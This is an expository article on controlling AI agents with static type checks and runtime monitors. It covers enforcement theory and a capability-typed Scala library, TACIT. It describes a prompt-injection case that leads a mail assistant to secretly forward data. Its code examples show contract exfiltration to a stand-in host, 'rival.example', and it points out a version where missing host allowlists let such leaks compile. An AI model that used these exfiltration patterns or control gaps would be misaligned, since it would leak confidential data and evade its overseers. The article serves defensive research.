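# Static types and runtime monitors for controlling AI agents: guarantees, overhead and coverage

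## What does it mean to check an agent's code beforehand or to watch it run?

An AI agent is a language model that carries out tasks for a person using tools such as a file store, a mail account or a payment service. The model only produces text. The software around it, called the harness, reads that text, performs the actions it describes and returns the results to the model. A developer can therefore limit the agent by putting the limits in the harness, where they apply no matter what the model writes.

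Agents need limits partly because they make mistakes and partly because outsiders can steer them. In a prompt injection, an attacker plants instructions in a document or an email, and the model follows them as if they came from its user. *Guardians of the Agents* (Meijer, 2025) describes an example with an assistant that can fetch and send mail. A user asks it to summarize her inbox. One message, disguised as a compliance notice, contains an instruction to send the summary to an outside address without mentioning it, and the assistant does so.

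Computer security had two ways to restrain programs long before AI agents existed. A static check accepts or rejects a program before it runs. A runtime monitor watches the program's actions as they happen and can block or change them.

### Single calls and whole programs

Most agents act by making one tool call at a time. The model writes a short record in JSON, a text format for structured data, with the name of a tool and its arguments:

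```
{"tool": "pay", "to": "Acme", "amount": 400}
```

The harness makes the payment and adds the result to the text in front of the model, which then writes its next call. Data going from one tool to another has to pass through the model. Anthropic's *Code execution with MCP* (2025) describes an agent that copies a meeting transcript from Google Drive into a Salesforce record. (MCP, the Model Context Protocol, is a standard for connecting agents to tools.) The model has to read the transcript and then write it out again, which for a two-hour meeting can add 50,000 tokens (the word fragments that models process).

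Alternatively, the model can write a program that makes the calls. Such agent code can loop over a hundred invoices, pass one tool's output straight to another and branch on what it finds without going back to the model. In *Code Mode*, Varda and Pai describe how Cloudflare turned its tools into functions in TypeScript, a typed version of JavaScript, and found that agents could handle more tools, and more complex ones, in that form. OpenAI's *Programmatic Tool Calling* documents a similar feature for JavaScript programs.

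Newer models are generally good at acting through programs. *The Bitter Lesson of Tool Calling* (Patel, Sen and colleagues, 2026) compared programs with JSON calls in 14 models released between November 2024 and July 2026. On 309 tasks from BFCL v4, a benchmark of tool calling, 11 of the 14 did at least as well with programs as with JSON calls. The other three were older OpenAI models that wrote the code for a line break where an actual line break belonged, which crashed their longer scripts. The test was narrow because its tools only returned their own arguments, so it measured whether a model called the right functions with the right arguments, not whether it finished a real job. Patel and colleagues also note that JSON calls still dominate in deployed systems. OpenAI advises developers to use single calls by default for actions that change something or need approval, because this keeps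 the point of authorisation clear. An agent built on that advice would sort invoices in a program and pay each one with a separate call.

The choice matters a great deal for static checking, because a harness can check a single call, such as whether the amount is a number, but not the call after it, which the model has not written yet. A program sets out in advance everything the agent might do until the program ends. Schneider, Morrisett and Harper, in *A Language-Based Approach to Security* (2001), describe program text as "a terse representation of all possible behaviors", which includes the branches that a given run never takes. Meijer's proposal depends on this. The model writes a whole workflow, and the harness verifies it before anything runs. Instructions planted in an email cannot change that workflow, because the model wrote it before the harness fetched any mail. They could still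 influence the next program if the model reads the first program's output before writing it, so the harness has to check every program.

### An office assistant and three policies

Take an office assistant that reads classified contracts, writes summaries of them and pays invoices. Odersky, Zhao and colleagues (2026), in *Tracking Capabilities for Safer Agents*, set out a similar scenario, in which an agent compares classified contracts and summarises what has changed without leaking their content. The assistant's employer lays down three policies:

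- (A) Contract text never reaches an outside party.
- (B) Payments to one recipient stay within 1,000 euros a day.
- (C) Every payment is eventually followed by a receipt.

A policy is a rule that separates acceptable program behaviour from unacceptable behaviour, and it can cover much more than file access. Schneider's *Enforceable Security Policies* (2000) gives examples from commerce, including a policy, close to policy C, that forbids runs in which a customer pays for a service and the seller does not provide it. Schneider formally treats a policy as a yes-or-no test on the whole set of runs a program could produce, because some policies, particularly those about leaks, depend on how one possible run compares with another.

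Here is a program that the assistant might write, in simplified Python:

```
contract = read_contract("acme")
summary = summarize(contract)
save("summaries/acme.txt", summary)

invoice = read_invoice("acme-117")
if invoice.amount <= 400:
    pay(invoice.recipient, invoice.amount)
    file_receipt(invoice)
```

The trace of a run is the sequence of security-relevant actions in it. If the invoice is for 350 euros, the trace is `read_contract`, `summarize`, `save`, `read_invoice`, `pay`, `file_receipt`. If it is for 900 euros, the trace stops after `read_invoice`. The program's code covers both cases, but an observer of a single run sees only one.

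It is unclear from these lines whether the program obeys policy A, because much depends on `summarize`. If that function sends the contract to a language model run by another company, the text may already have reached an outside party, even though the program mails nothing. Odersky and colleagues guard against this by treating the cloud-hosted model behind the agent as untrusted and having a separate, trusted model do the summarising.

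### What a type checker does

A type describes what a value is, and is available before the program runs. In some languages it also describes which effects the value can cause, such as writing to a file. A type checker is a static check that compares the types in a program and rejects the program if they do not fit. At its simplest, it catches mistakes such as `pay("Acme", "four hundred")`, which has text where a number belongs.

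The same mechanism can serve policy A if contracts get a type of their own:

```
def read_contract(name: str) -> Classified
def send_email(to: str, body: str) -> None

text = read_contract("acme")
send_email("sales@rival.example", text)   # rejected
```

The first two lines declare that `read_contract` returns a value of type `Classified` and that `send_email` accepts only ordinary text, here `str`. The last line uses a `Classified` value where ordinary text is required, so the checker rejects the whole program. The harness never opens the contract, and the check doesn't depend on its contents.

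This works only if agent code cannot unwrap a `Classified` value and mail its contents. Odersky and colleagues prevent this using the language Scala, whose type system can track capabilities, the values a program must hold to use a resource such as a file or the network. Agent code may compute on a contract only with functions that hold no capabilities.

But types catch no errors unless something checks them. In the experiment by Patel and colleagues, the tools also came with typed descriptions, which showed the model how to call each function. The harness ran the scripts without checking their types first, and faulty ones failed when they ran.

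### What a runtime monitor does

A monitor leaves the program as it is and stands between the program and its effects. For policy B it can be very short:

```
paid_today = {}   # euros per recipient, emptied at midnight

def guarded_pay(to, amount):
    total = paid_today.get(to, 0) + amount
    if total > 1000:
        raise Blocked("daily limit")
    pay(to, amount)
    paid_today[to] = total
```

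The agent's code gets `guarded_pay` instead of `pay`. Suppose the agent pays Acme 600 euros in the morning and tries to pay another 500 in the afternoon. The monitor adds the two amounts and blocks the second payment because the total of 1,100 euros is over the limit. The first payment has already gone through, correctly, since it broke no rule.

Schneider describes a monitor as a small machine that keeps a state in memory, which in the example above is the table of payments. Before each step of the program, the monitor checks the step against its state. If the policy allows the step, the program takes it and the monitor updates its state; otherwise the monitor stops the program. Monitors for agents may respond more mildly. In Meijer's version, an attempt to mail a summary to an outside domain puts the monitor into an error state, and the harness can then either end the workflow or alert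 the user.

### Soundness and false rejections

A mechanism is sound for a policy if nothing it accepts can violate that policy. `guarded_pay` is sound for policy B only if agent code cannot reach the bank any other way. The type checker is sound for policy A only if every route to the outside world has a type that excludes `Classified` values, so a single forgotten function is enough to make it unsound.

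Soundness alone is easy to get, because a harness that refuses everything is perfectly sound. The price is false rejections, refusals of programs or actions that would have obeyed the policy. For a static check of general programs some of these are unavoidable, for a reason that Morris (1973), in *Protection in Programming Languages*, already pointed out. He wanted to prove that a value never leaves a certain part of a program, and observed that no complete set of rules can do it, since one can write a program in which the value stays put only if some other, arbitrary computation comes to an end. No general method can tell whether an arbitrary computation ends. The assistant's code could run into the same difficulty:

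```
if long_search_succeeds():
    send_email("sales@rival.example", contract_text)
```

If the search never succeeds, the program is harmless. No checker can determine this for every program, so a checker that always gives an answer and never accepts a program that leaks must reject some harmless ones.

Monitors also block harmless actions when their rule is cruder than the policy. Schneider's standard example is a monitor that blocks all messages once the program has read a file. Applied to contracts, this rule would enforce policy A as long as messages were the only way for information to leave. But after opening one contract, the assistant could not send a colleague a lunch invitation.

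### Origins

The reference monitor dates from the early 1970s, when the US Air Force wanted people with different security clearances to share one computer. Its advisers worried about a malicious user who was authorised to use the machine and could run any program on it. They proposed a mechanism that checks each attempt by a program to use data, a device or another program against a list of what the user may do. It had to be tamper-proof, run on every access, and be small enough for people to analyse and test completely. Type checking became a security mechanism more gradually. In 1973 Morris proposed "seals", which let a program seal a value so that other programs could pass it around but not look inside, much like the `Classified` type above. He wanted programmers to be able to prove things about their own code without reading everyone else's, but his seals were tags that the machine checked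 at run time. A decade later Strom, in *Mechanisms for Compile-Time Enforcement of Security*, described an IBM language whose compiler checked the sequence of operations on each variable along every path through a program, so that security added as little work as possible at run time. Java and .NET brought checks before the run into wide use. As Meijer points out, both verify the types in compiled code before executing it, but check whether array indexes are in range only at run time. By 2001 Schneider and colleagues could distinguish two schools of research, one that rewrote programs to contain their own monitors and one that started from type-safe languages. They noted that actual systems always combined rewriting with analysis.

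### The case for each method

Odersky and colleagues claim four advantages for a type system tailored to agents. It catches errors before the program runs, so the line that mails the contract never executes. It adds no monitoring overhead, because checking finishes before the program starts. Its guarantees hold for all inputs, not only tested ones, so they cover any contract the assistant reads, including one in which an attacker has planted instructions. It is also modular, so developers can check components such as the wrapper for contracts and the summarising tool separately, then build a safe environment out of them.

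One argument for monitors is that they can use information that becomes available only during the run. Before the run, `invoice.amount` is known only to be a number, but when the program requests the payment, the monitor has the actual figure, say 350 euros. A monitor can also keep a history that includes payments a different program made that morning. Schneider and colleagues write that a security decision might depend on the machine's current state and its past execution, among other things.

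Monitors also place few requirements on the code. A guard on the payment tool works the same way whether the request comes from Scala, JavaScript or a single JSON call, and it doesn't need added types, a particular language or even the source code. *Toward Safe LLM Agents* (Dantas, Nowroozi and colleagues, 2026), a review of 38 studies, calls runtime monitoring the most mature way of enforcing safety in agents, although the guarantees it found cover only single steps or short stretches of a task. OpenAI tells developers to check arguments and permissions on every call in their own application, even when the call comes from a program that OpenAI runs in an isolated environment.

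## Which policies can each method enforce in principle?

Some policies can't be enforced by any monitor, and others can't be enforced by any static check, however well built. Theorists usually compare the two methods by exact enforcement, which requires a mechanism to be sound and to leave alone every program or run that obeys the policy. A harness that refuses everything fails the second requirement. What each method can enforce depends mainly on the kind of policy.

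### Safety, liveness and comparisons between runs

A policy is a safety property if every violation shows up after finitely many actions of a single run. The limit of 1,000 euros a day is an example, because a run violates it with the payment that takes the total over the limit, and nothing the program does later can undo the violation.

A liveness property requires that something good eventually happens, such as a program filing a receipt after each payment. However long the program has gone without filing the receipt, it could still do so in its next step, so no finite part of a run proves a violation.

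Other policies apply to a program's whole set of possible runs rather than to each run separately. Suppose one program emails a supplier "yes" or "no" at random, while another emails "yes" only if a classified contract contains a penalty clause. Only the second program leaks, yet each of its runs is also a possible run of the first. Detecting the leak requires comparing runs with different contracts to see that the message depends on the contract. In Schneider's terms, the set of all conceivable runs satisfies a policy against leaks, because no value in it depends on any other, but a subset may violate the policy. By contrast, removing runs from a set never causes it to violate a safety property.

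### What a monitor can do by halting a program

Schneider's theorem concerns monitors that watch a run and can only stop it. They enforce safety properties at most. The proof works out what such a monitor has to go on. Let S be the set of runs a program can produce, and let p be the test that the monitor applies to a run. The monitor sees only one run, so the policy P must amount to testing each run separately:

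```
P(S) is true exactly when p(s) is true for every run s in S
```

This already rules out policies that compare runs. The monitor also cannot see the future. If the run so far fails the test, the monitor cannot let it continue in the hope of a better ending, because the program might stop right there. A failed beginning must therefore spoil everything that could follow it:

```
if p(t) is false for a finite run t,
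then p(t followed by u) is false for every u
```

Finally, the monitor has to reject a bad run after a finite time:

```
if p(s) is false, then p is false for some finite beginning of s
```

A policy that meets all three conditions is a safety property.

However, a monitor cannot enforce every safety property. One example is the rule that no user waits more than a fixed number of seconds for a resource. This is a safety property because any violation shows up in finite time, but halting the program cannot prevent the violation, since time keeps passing. If the rule counts program steps instead of seconds, the monitor can enforce it, since a halted program takes no more steps.

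### Exact static checks compared with monitors

*Computability Classes for Enforcement Mechanisms* (Hamlen, Morrisett and Schneider, 2006) describes static checks and monitors in one mathematical model. It represents programs as Turing machines, the standard idealisation of a computer. Each machine reads input that arrives only during the run and writes its security-relevant events on a separate tape, which the enforcement mechanism can read.

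They prove that static checks can exactly enforce the decidable properties of programs and no others. A property is decidable if some procedure correctly answers yes or no for every program in finite time. The proof is immediate, because an exact static check is such a procedure. Whether a program eventually stops is undecidable, but whether it stops within 100 steps is decidable, because it can read at most 100 input symbols in that time and a checker can try every input of that length.

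For monitors the bound is wider, namely the co-recursively enumerable properties. A property belongs to this class if some procedure detects every violating program in finite time, though it may search forever when the program is innocent. The proof has two directions:

- Start with a policy that meets Schneider's conditions and a test p that a computer can carry out. A procedure can go through all finite beginnings of the program's runs and test each one. If the program can violate the policy, the procedure eventually reaches a beginning that fails. Otherwise it goes on forever.
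- Start instead with a procedure that halts on exactly the violating programs. After the n-th event of a run, the monitor applies the procedure to the program's text for n steps, and it rejects the run if the procedure has halted by then. Every violating program fails this test sooner or later, and no obedient program ever does.

Monitors can enforce every decidable property, because a monitor can run the whole static check as soon as the program is loaded. They can also enforce some undecidable properties, so by this measure they are strictly more powerful than static checks.

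Hamlen and colleagues illustrate the gap with the boot sector of a disk, which holds the code that starts the computer. Say that it occupies cells 0 to 511, and that the policy forbids programs to write there. A monitor needs one comparison per write:

```
def guarded_write(cell, data):
    if 0 <= cell <= 511:
        raise Blocked("boot sector")
    disk.write(cell, data)
```

No static check can decide the same policy exactly. For any computation at all, someone can write this program:

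```
run(computation)       # may never finish
disk.write(0, data)    # reached only if it does finish
```

Morris raised the same difficulty about leaks. A checker that was right about every such program could determine whether an arbitrary computation ends, which Turing proved impossible in 1936. The monitor does not need to determine this. It waits while the computation runs, and if the computation never ends, the program never reaches the forbidden write.

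### Why the theorem does not settle the choice

Static checks in practical use enforce a decidable policy that is stricter than the intended one. For the boot sector, a checker could accept only programs in which every write names a fixed cell numbered 512 or higher. This is sound and fast, but it rejects any program that calculates its cell numbers, even correctly. Hamlen and colleagues give the example of a checker that replaces "eventually stops" with "stops within 100 steps", and so rejects a program that stops after 101. The theorem does not show how many false rejections there will be among the programs that models write for real tasks, or what happens after a rejection. If a model can quickly rewrite the program in a form that the checker accepts, the rejection does little harm.

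A checker can also require more than the code. In proof-carrying code, a technique from the 1990s, the supplier attaches a proof that the program obeys the policy, and the recipient only has to verify the proof. Hamlen and colleagues note that some policies that are undecidable for code alone become decidable for pairs of code and proof. Type annotations provide some of the same help, since the checker doesn't have to work out what the programmer intended.

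The comparison also depends on the model's assumption that the monitor can read the full text of the program it watches, which is why it can do anything that a static check can. Actual monitors make little use of that text. Those in operating systems typically look at one instruction at a time. Hamlen and colleagues point out that if the static check gets the source code and the monitor gets a compiled version with some information missing, each might enforce policies that the other cannot. Agent harnesses are usually in this position. For example, a guard on the payment tool receives the recipient and amount but not the program that requested the payment, while a type checker has the program but not the invoices.

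The same paper lists practical differences unrelated to computability. Besides slowing the program, a monitor may detect a violation arbitrarily late and only on some runs, so the system may have to undo a half-finished computation. This matters a great deal for an agent that has already sent three of five emails when the monitor stops it. However, some policies that a static check could enforce are simpler to enforce with a monitor, which lowers the risk of mistakes in the enforcement mechanism.

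### Rewriting the program

A harness can also change a program before running it. A program rewriter takes any program M and produces a new program R(M) in finite time. Hamlen and colleagues require two things of it:

```
R(M) obeys the policy, for every program M
if M already obeys the policy, then R(M) is equivalent to M
```

The first condition is soundness, and the second preserves the behavior of programs that already obey the policy. "Equivalent" has to allow some differences, such as extra steps for security checks. If it meant "identical", rewriting could enforce no more policies than a static check can. Rewriting is often used to insert a monitor's checks into the program, for example by replacing `disk.write` with `guarded_write`.

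Rewriting can also enforce policies that no monitor can. Suppose that a directory contains a secret file, and that programs may list the directory but the policy requires them to behave exactly as they would if the file were not there. To detect a violation, a monitor would have to compare the actual run with a hypothetical run in which the file is missing. Even if the monitor ran both versions side by side, it might have to wait forever to learn whether they are equivalent, because two runs can be equivalent overall without matching step by step.

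A rewriter changes every request for the directory listing so that the result leaves out the secret file, and doesn't need to detect anything to do so. Programs that would have reacted to the file no longer can, and the rest behave as before. A harness can achieve the same effect without editing the agent's code by giving it a filtered listing tool. The tool works by changing what the program receives, which Schneider's halting monitors cannot do, although its developer might also call it a monitor.

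Rewriting also cannot enforce some policies, such as requiring that a program stop on at least one input. If a rewriter could enforce this, we could use the rewritten program to determine whether the original ever stops, which is undecidable.

Hamlen and colleagues also used the two conditions to correct the earlier result on monitors. The co-recursively enumerable class is only an upper bound on the policies that monitors can enforce, partly because a monitor's own response must obey the policy. For example, a monitor that can only terminate programs cannot enforce a ban on termination.

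A monitor may also recognise a violation too late to prevent it. For example, a service might lend a resource to a program and be unable to take it back. Once the program announces that it has finished, the service lends the resource to another program. The policy forbids the first program from using the resource after its announcement. A monitor can recognise a forbidden use, but by then both programs have the resource. To prevent this, the monitor would have to block false announcements, but no general method can predict whether a program will ever use the resource again. Hamlen and colleagues conclude that the policies monitors can really enforce are the co-recursively enumerable ones that a rewriter can also enforce.

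### Monitors that edit the run

Schneider's monitors respond to a violation by halting the program. Ligatti, Bauer and Walker (2003), in *Edit Automata*, asked what monitors gain from milder responses. They describe a monitor as a machine that receives the program's actions and may change the sequence before passing it on to the outside world. A truncation automaton can only stop the program. A suppression automaton can stop it or drop individual actions, and an insertion automaton can stop it or add actions. An edit automaton can do all three.

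They require each machine to be sound and transparent. A transparent machine preserves the meaning of runs that already obey the policy. The results depend on how strictly one interprets transparency.

Under the strict reading, the monitor must pass on each action of an obedient run before it looks at the next. If nothing restricts in advance what programs may do, all four machines then enforce exactly the safety properties, so the ability to edit doesn't let a monitor enforce more policies. When the run so far breaks the policy but a later action could repair it, the monitor has to alter the run immediately, in case the program stops there. If the program then makes the repair, the monitor has altered a run that was acceptable as a whole.

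Under the looser reading, the monitor may delay actions, and its output only has to be equivalent to the original run. An edit automaton can then enforce any policy that a computer can test on a single run. It holds back actions until the sequence so far obeys the policy, then releases them.

Ligatti and colleagues describe a market in which customers take apples and pay for them, in either order, and every purchase must be complete. If a customer pays first, the automaton holds back the payment while the customer browses, then releases both actions together when the customer takes the apples. If a customer takes apples and does anything other than pay for them next, the automaton issues a warning and stops. The automaton needs both suppression and insertion. For example, a monitor that could only insert actions couldn't handle an early payment. It couldn't let the payment through, because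 the customer might never take the apples, and it couldn't insert the "take" action, because the customer might be about to take them anyway.

The result on edit automata covers only finite runs, which is a strong assumption. Hamlen and colleagues observe that if all runs were finite, every mechanism in their model could enforce as much, because it could list a program's runs beforehand and test them. The more serious difficulty for agents is that the automaton must be able to hold actions back. Ligatti and colleagues say that the strict reading is often the right one for interactive programs, where an action has to return a value before the program can continue. Most tool calls work this way. For example, a program that searches a mailbox needs the results before it can use them.

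### Actions that cannot be undone

Ray (2026), in *What Can Be Enforced?*, adapts this theory to agents that send mail, move money and call outside services. Ray's monitor is a gate in front of each tool call. It must allow the call, block it or substitute another one before the call takes effect, and it cannot undo a call it has allowed. Ray uses the strict meaning of transparency, so the gate may not block or change any action in a run that obeys the policy.

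The gate can also run a fixed set of yes-or-no checks on a call, such as whether an email contains personal data. For the main theorem, Ray assumes that these checks are always correct, and treats the errors of real classifiers separately. The gate's memory is limited to a finite number of internal states, registers for data such as names, and counters, including a separate set for each key, such as each recipient.

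The theorem is that such a gate enforces exactly the safety policies that permit at least one run and whose acceptable beginnings it can recognise with this memory and these questions. One half of the proof is to construct a gate that tracks the run so far and blocks any call that would make it unacceptable. Blocking is always permissible under a safety policy because it has no outside effect.

For the other half, suppose that a gate enforces a policy that is not a safety property. Then some infinite run breaks the policy even though each of its finite beginnings can be continued into a run that obeys the policy. If the gate receives the calls of this bad run one at a time, transparency requires it to allow each call, because the calls up to and including that one also begin a run that obeys the policy. The gate therefore allows the entire bad run, which contradicts soundness. The part about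 memory follows because the gate itself recognises the acceptable beginnings, which are the sequences it lets through unchanged.

Ray then shows that gates enforce strictly less than edit automata, using the policy that every payment is eventually followed by a confirmation. An edit automaton holds the payment until the confirmation arrives. A gate must allow or block the payment immediately. If it blocks the payment, it interferes with a program that was about to confirm. If it allows the payment and no confirmation follows, the payment can't be reversed. Replacing the payment doesn't help either, because a different action would change a run that complies with the policy, and an equivalent payment would be just as irreversible. The proof doesn't depend on the gate's capability, so using a more capable model as the gate would not remove the limit.

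### Policies with counters

A policy that can never block anything probably contains a mistake, so a developer may want to check for this. Ray proves that no program can perform this check for every policy in a language with two counters that can be incremented, decremented and tested for zero. Such counters can simulate a Minsky machine, a simple computer that can carry out any computation. The proof builds a policy that blocks something exactly when a given Minsky machine halts, and the halting problem for Minsky machines is undecidable.

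The gate can still enforce the policy in such a case, because it only has to update its counters after each call and check whether the next call is forbidden. It does this for the sequence of calls that actually occurs, so it doesn't have to answer the undecidable question, which is about all possible sequences.

Ray also identifies a simpler policy language in which it is decidable whether a policy can ever fire. In this language, counters can only go up, rules compare counters only with fixed numbers, and one recipient's counters don't affect another's. The problem is then in PSPACE, which means that an algorithm can solve it using memory polynomial in the size of the input, though this can still take a very long time in the worst case.

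Two simplifications make the analysis possible. First, with a limit of 1,000 euros per recipient, the analysis can treat all totals above 1,000 as the same, because a total never decreases. If payments are in whole euros, it has to distinguish only 1,002 values: 0 to 1,000, and "more". Second, it needs to consider only one recipient. If payments to many recipients break the limit, the payments to the recipient whose total exceeds it would break it on their own.

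The language can express spending caps, quotas and the rule that an agent sends nothing after its user has revoked access. It can also express daily limits. The `guarded_pay` function from the office example empties its table at midnight, which makes the totals go down. Ray avoids this by keeping a separate counter for each recipient on each day. The gate then needs a trusted clock to attach the right day to each payment.

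### The three office policies

The table below classifies the office assistant's policies according to these results. The last column assumes a gate that acts before each call and cannot delay or undo the call.

| Policy | Kind | Exact static check | Exact gate |
|---|---|---|---|
| A: contract text never reaches an outside party | comparison between runs, if any leak counts | no | no |
| B: at most 1,000 euros a day per recipient | safety | no | yes |
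| C: every payment is eventually followed by a receipt | liveness | no | no |

What policy A forbids depends on what counts as contract text. If only recognisable passages count, sending one is a bad event in a single run, so the policy is a safety property. A gate could enforce it given a perfect test for whether a message contains contract text. But the program that emails "yes" when a contract has a penalty clause would pass, since it sends no contract text. If the employer wants to prevent that too, outside messages must not depend on the contracts in any way, and no monitor that observes one run at a time can enforce this exactly.

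A monitor can enforce something stricter than the policy, as Schneider notes of leaks generally. The earlier rule that blocks all messages once the program has opened a contract is one such safety property. The `Classified` type is also stricter than the policy, but it is a rule about the program's text, so it rejects a program that would mail a contract only in a branch that never runs. The trick with the secret file does not apply directly here, because the assistant has to read the contracts to summarise them.

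Policy B is the clearest case for a monitor, and it is nearly the same as one of Ray's own examples. As with the boot sector, a static check cannot decide it, because a program might pay 1,001 euros after a computation that may never end. Even for simple programs, the check lacks information about other runs. A good checker could prove that the assistant's program from the first section pays an invoice only if the amount is at most 400 euros, but three runs on the same day could still pay one recipient 1,200 euros. The harness could allow only two runs a day, but it would then need a monitor to count them.

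Neither method can enforce Policy C exactly. A program may pay, start a computation that might never end, and file the receipt afterwards, so a static check would have to determine whether the computation ends. A halting monitor can make things worse, because stopping the program after the payment prevents the receipt. Replacing "eventually" with "within ten steps" turns the policy into a safety property, which the monitor can enforce by halting the program after the tenth step, but this still leaves the payment without a receipt.

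The checker could do better with a stricter static rule that accepts only programs in which `file_receipt` comes directly after every `pay`, as it does in the assistant's program. This rule would wrongly reject a program that pays ten invoices and then files ten receipts. It would also depend on conditions that no check of the program can establish, such as the machine not failing between the two calls.

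An edit automaton could hold each payment until the program files the receipt, but if the receipt has to include a transaction number from the bank, the program can't file it until the payment goes through, so neither would happen. The automaton could instead make the payment, file the receipt itself immediately, and drop the program's own receipt when it comes. Ligatti and colleagues describe this technique of inserting a required action and later suppressing the original. It works if the monitor has the information to write the receipt and if the receipt can be filed earlier than the program intended. Developers can get much the same result by replacing the agent's `pay` tool with a single tool that pays and files the receipt.

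## How does a type checker restrict code written by an agent?

The `Classified` type in the office example is a simplified version of one in TACIT (Tracked Agent Capabilities In Types), which Odersky and colleagues built at EPFL. TACIT is an MCP server, so existing agents such as Claude Code can connect to it. The agent sends Scala code to the server, which compiles it against a small library for accessing files, running commands and using the network. The server runs the code only if the compiler accepts all of it. Otherwise, the agent gets the compiler's error messages and can try again. The agent can be written in any language, because TACIT checks only the code the agent sends.

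The assistant needs code that works on contracts, so the compiler has to distinguish functions that only compute a result from functions that could also pass on the contract text.

### Capabilities and capture sets

TACIT's capabilities include `FileSystem` for opening files and `Network` for contacting websites. A program can store capabilities or pass them to functions like any other value, but agent code has to get them from the library and can't make its own.

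It is not enough to look at which capabilities a program passes to a function, because the function may already have one inside it:

```
val shout = (s: String) => s.toUpperCase
val store = (s: String) => file.write(s)
```

Both functions take a text as their only argument. `shout` returns it in capitals, while `store` writes it to a file that it picked up from the surrounding program. An ordinary type for `store` would not mention the file. Scala's capture checking, an experimental extension of the language, adds this information as a capture set, which lists the capabilities that a value may hold:

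```
shout: String -> String
store: String ->{file} Unit
```

`Unit` means the function returns no useful value. The plain arrow `->` marks a pure function, which holds no capabilities and so has no side effects. The double arrow `=>` marks a function that may hold any capabilities. For other values, the set of capabilities follows a caret. `Logger^{file}` is a logger that may use `file`, `Logger^` may use any capability, and `Logger` holds none.

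The compiler works out a function's capture set from the capabilities its body mentions, so the set can include some that the function never uses. If `store` wrote to the file only after a search that never succeeds, its type would still list `file`. The checker therefore doesn't have to determine whether the search succeeds, but it rejects some safe code.

A value with a smaller capture set is acceptable wherever the program allows a larger one. In the notation of type theory, `A <: B` means that A is a subtype of B, so a value of type A can stand in for a value of type B. Leaving aside a special rule for class parameters, the order is:

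```
T^C <: T^D   if D covers C

D covers C   if every capability c in C is in D,
             or D covers the capture set of c
```

The last line is there because most capabilities get their power from others. If a logger `lg` writes to a file `out`, it can do nothing that `out` doesn't allow, so `{out}` covers `{lg}`. Scala's *Tracked Capabilities Overview* gives the resulting order for such a logger and an unrelated capability `f`:

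```
A <: A^{lg} <: A^{out} <: A^{out, f} <: A^
```

Now suppose that some part of the library accepts only pure functions, whose capture sets must be empty. The compiler accepts `shout` there but rejects `store`, because the empty set does not cover `{file}`. The empty set contains neither `file` nor the file system in `file`'s own capture set, nor the universal capability from which all others derive.

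### Keeping a capability inside its block

Agent code gets access to files by calling `requestFileSystem`, which grants it for one directory and for the duration of one block of code. In simplified form, its declaration is:

```
def requestFileSystem[T](root: String)(block: FileSystem^ => T): T
```

The function creates a capability for the directory `root`, passes it to the block and returns the block's result, which can have any type `T`. A program might try to keep its access for longer by returning a function that holds the capability:

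```
val later = requestFileSystem("/office") { fs =>
  () => fs.access("/office/notes.txt").read()
}
later()
```

This block doesn't read the file. It returns a function that would read it when called, after the block has ended. Scala's *Capture Checking Basics* explains the compiler's reasoning for a similar program, and the same steps apply here:

- `fs` has the type `FileSystem^`, so it is a capability.
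- The returned function uses `fs`, so its type is `() ->{fs} String`.
- `T` would have to be this type. But `T` is also the type of `later`, which the program defines outside the block, where `fs` does not exist.
- The capture set in `T` therefore cannot include `fs`, and the compiler reports an error.

Assigning the function to a variable outside the block fails for the same reason. The checker can also distinguish between programs that look almost identical. For example, a block might write each number in a list to a log file and return the squares. The checker accepts this for an ordinary list, because all the writing happens inside the block. It rejects the same code for a lazy list, which computes each element only when the program needs it, possibly after the log file has closed.

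Models write code that breaks these rules, and some of that code is harmless. In the tests by Odersky and colleagues, one program tried to return a list of file entries from its block, and the compiler rejected it because each entry held the file system. Another program had a function that printed the first five lines of a file and declared its parameter as `FileEntry`. Without the caret, that type means an entry that holds no capabilities, so the compiler rejected the program, although it would have done no harm.

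With `requestFileSystem`, the type shows that a program has access to some directory, but not which one. The library therefore compares each path with `root` at run time and raises an error if the path lies outside it. The software company VirtusLab points out in *Safe Scala an introduction* that safe Scala code still relies on run-time checks in the library that the code has to use. These checks are in effect a small monitor, and the type system makes sure that agent code cannot bypass it.

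### Policy A in code

To keep contract text from outside parties, as policy A requires, the employer marks the contracts directory as classified in TACIT, and the library then returns the contents of its files only in a wrapper:

```
trait Classified[T]:
  def map[U](op: T -> U): Classified[U]
```

Agent code cannot take the content out of its wrapper. It can only pass a function to `map`, which applies the function to the content and wraps the result. The single arrow in the declaration means the function must be pure.

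The compiler accepts the following program, which summarises a contract. The function `chat` sends a request to a second language model, which the employer trusts. TACIT passes capabilities implicitly, so `fs` no longer appears.

```
val summary = requestFileSystem("/office") {
  val contract = readClassified("/office/contracts/acme.txt")
  val request = contract.map(text => s"Summarise this: $text")
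  val result = chat(request)
  writeClassified("/office/contracts/acme-summary.txt", result)
  result
}
println(summary)
```

The compiler goes through it as follows:

- `readClassified` requires a `FileSystem`, which the block provides. It returns a `Classified[String]`, a wrapped text.
- The function passed to `map` puts a short instruction in front of the contract. It mentions no capability, so its type is `String -> String` and `map` accepts it.
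- `chat` accepts a wrapped request and returns a wrapped answer.
- `writeClassified` accepts the wrapped answer. The library checks during the run that the target file is classified too.
- The block returns a `Classified[String]`, which holds no capabilities, so it may leave the block.
- `println` accepts any value. For a wrapped one, the agent gets only the placeholder `Classified(****)`.

The next program tries to send the contract to a competitor:

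```
requestNetwork(Set("rival.example")) {
  requestFileSystem("/office") {
    val contract = readClassified("/office/contracts/acme.txt")
    contract.map(text => httpPost("https://rival.example/in", text))
  }
}
```

`httpPost` requires a `Network` capability. The function passed to `map` captures this capability, `net`, from the outer block, so its type is `String ->{net} String`. `map` requires a function with an empty capture set, but this function's capture set is `{net}`, so the compiler reports a type mismatch and rejects the whole program.

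Some obvious variations also fail. Calling `httpPost` directly on the wrapped contract is an ordinary type error, since `httpPost` expects a `String`. Converting the contract to a string compiles, but produces only the placeholder. Requesting network access inside `map` also fails, because `requestNetwork` itself requires a capability. The program can test for a penalty clause inside `map`, but the result is a `Classified[Boolean]`, which it can't use to decide whether to email "yes" to a supplier.

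The guarantee depends on which functions the library offers, and these have changed. Glama's *TACIT*, a copy of the project's later documentation in a directory of MCP servers, describes a new function, `httpPostClassified`, that sends a wrapped text to a permitted website and wraps the reply. A company could use it to process contracts with an outside service. The employer can list the permitted hosts in the server's settings. Without this list, the only limit is the one in the program's `requestNetwork` call, which the agent writes, so an agent could name `rival.example` and send the contract there in a program that compiles. An employer who wants policy A under this version has to set the list, which the library enforces at run time.

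### The second model and the two output channels

Another company usually hosts the untrusted model behind the assistant, and Odersky and colleagues assume that this model may even cooperate fully with an attacker. The model writes the program, including the function inside `map`, but never receives the text that the function processes.

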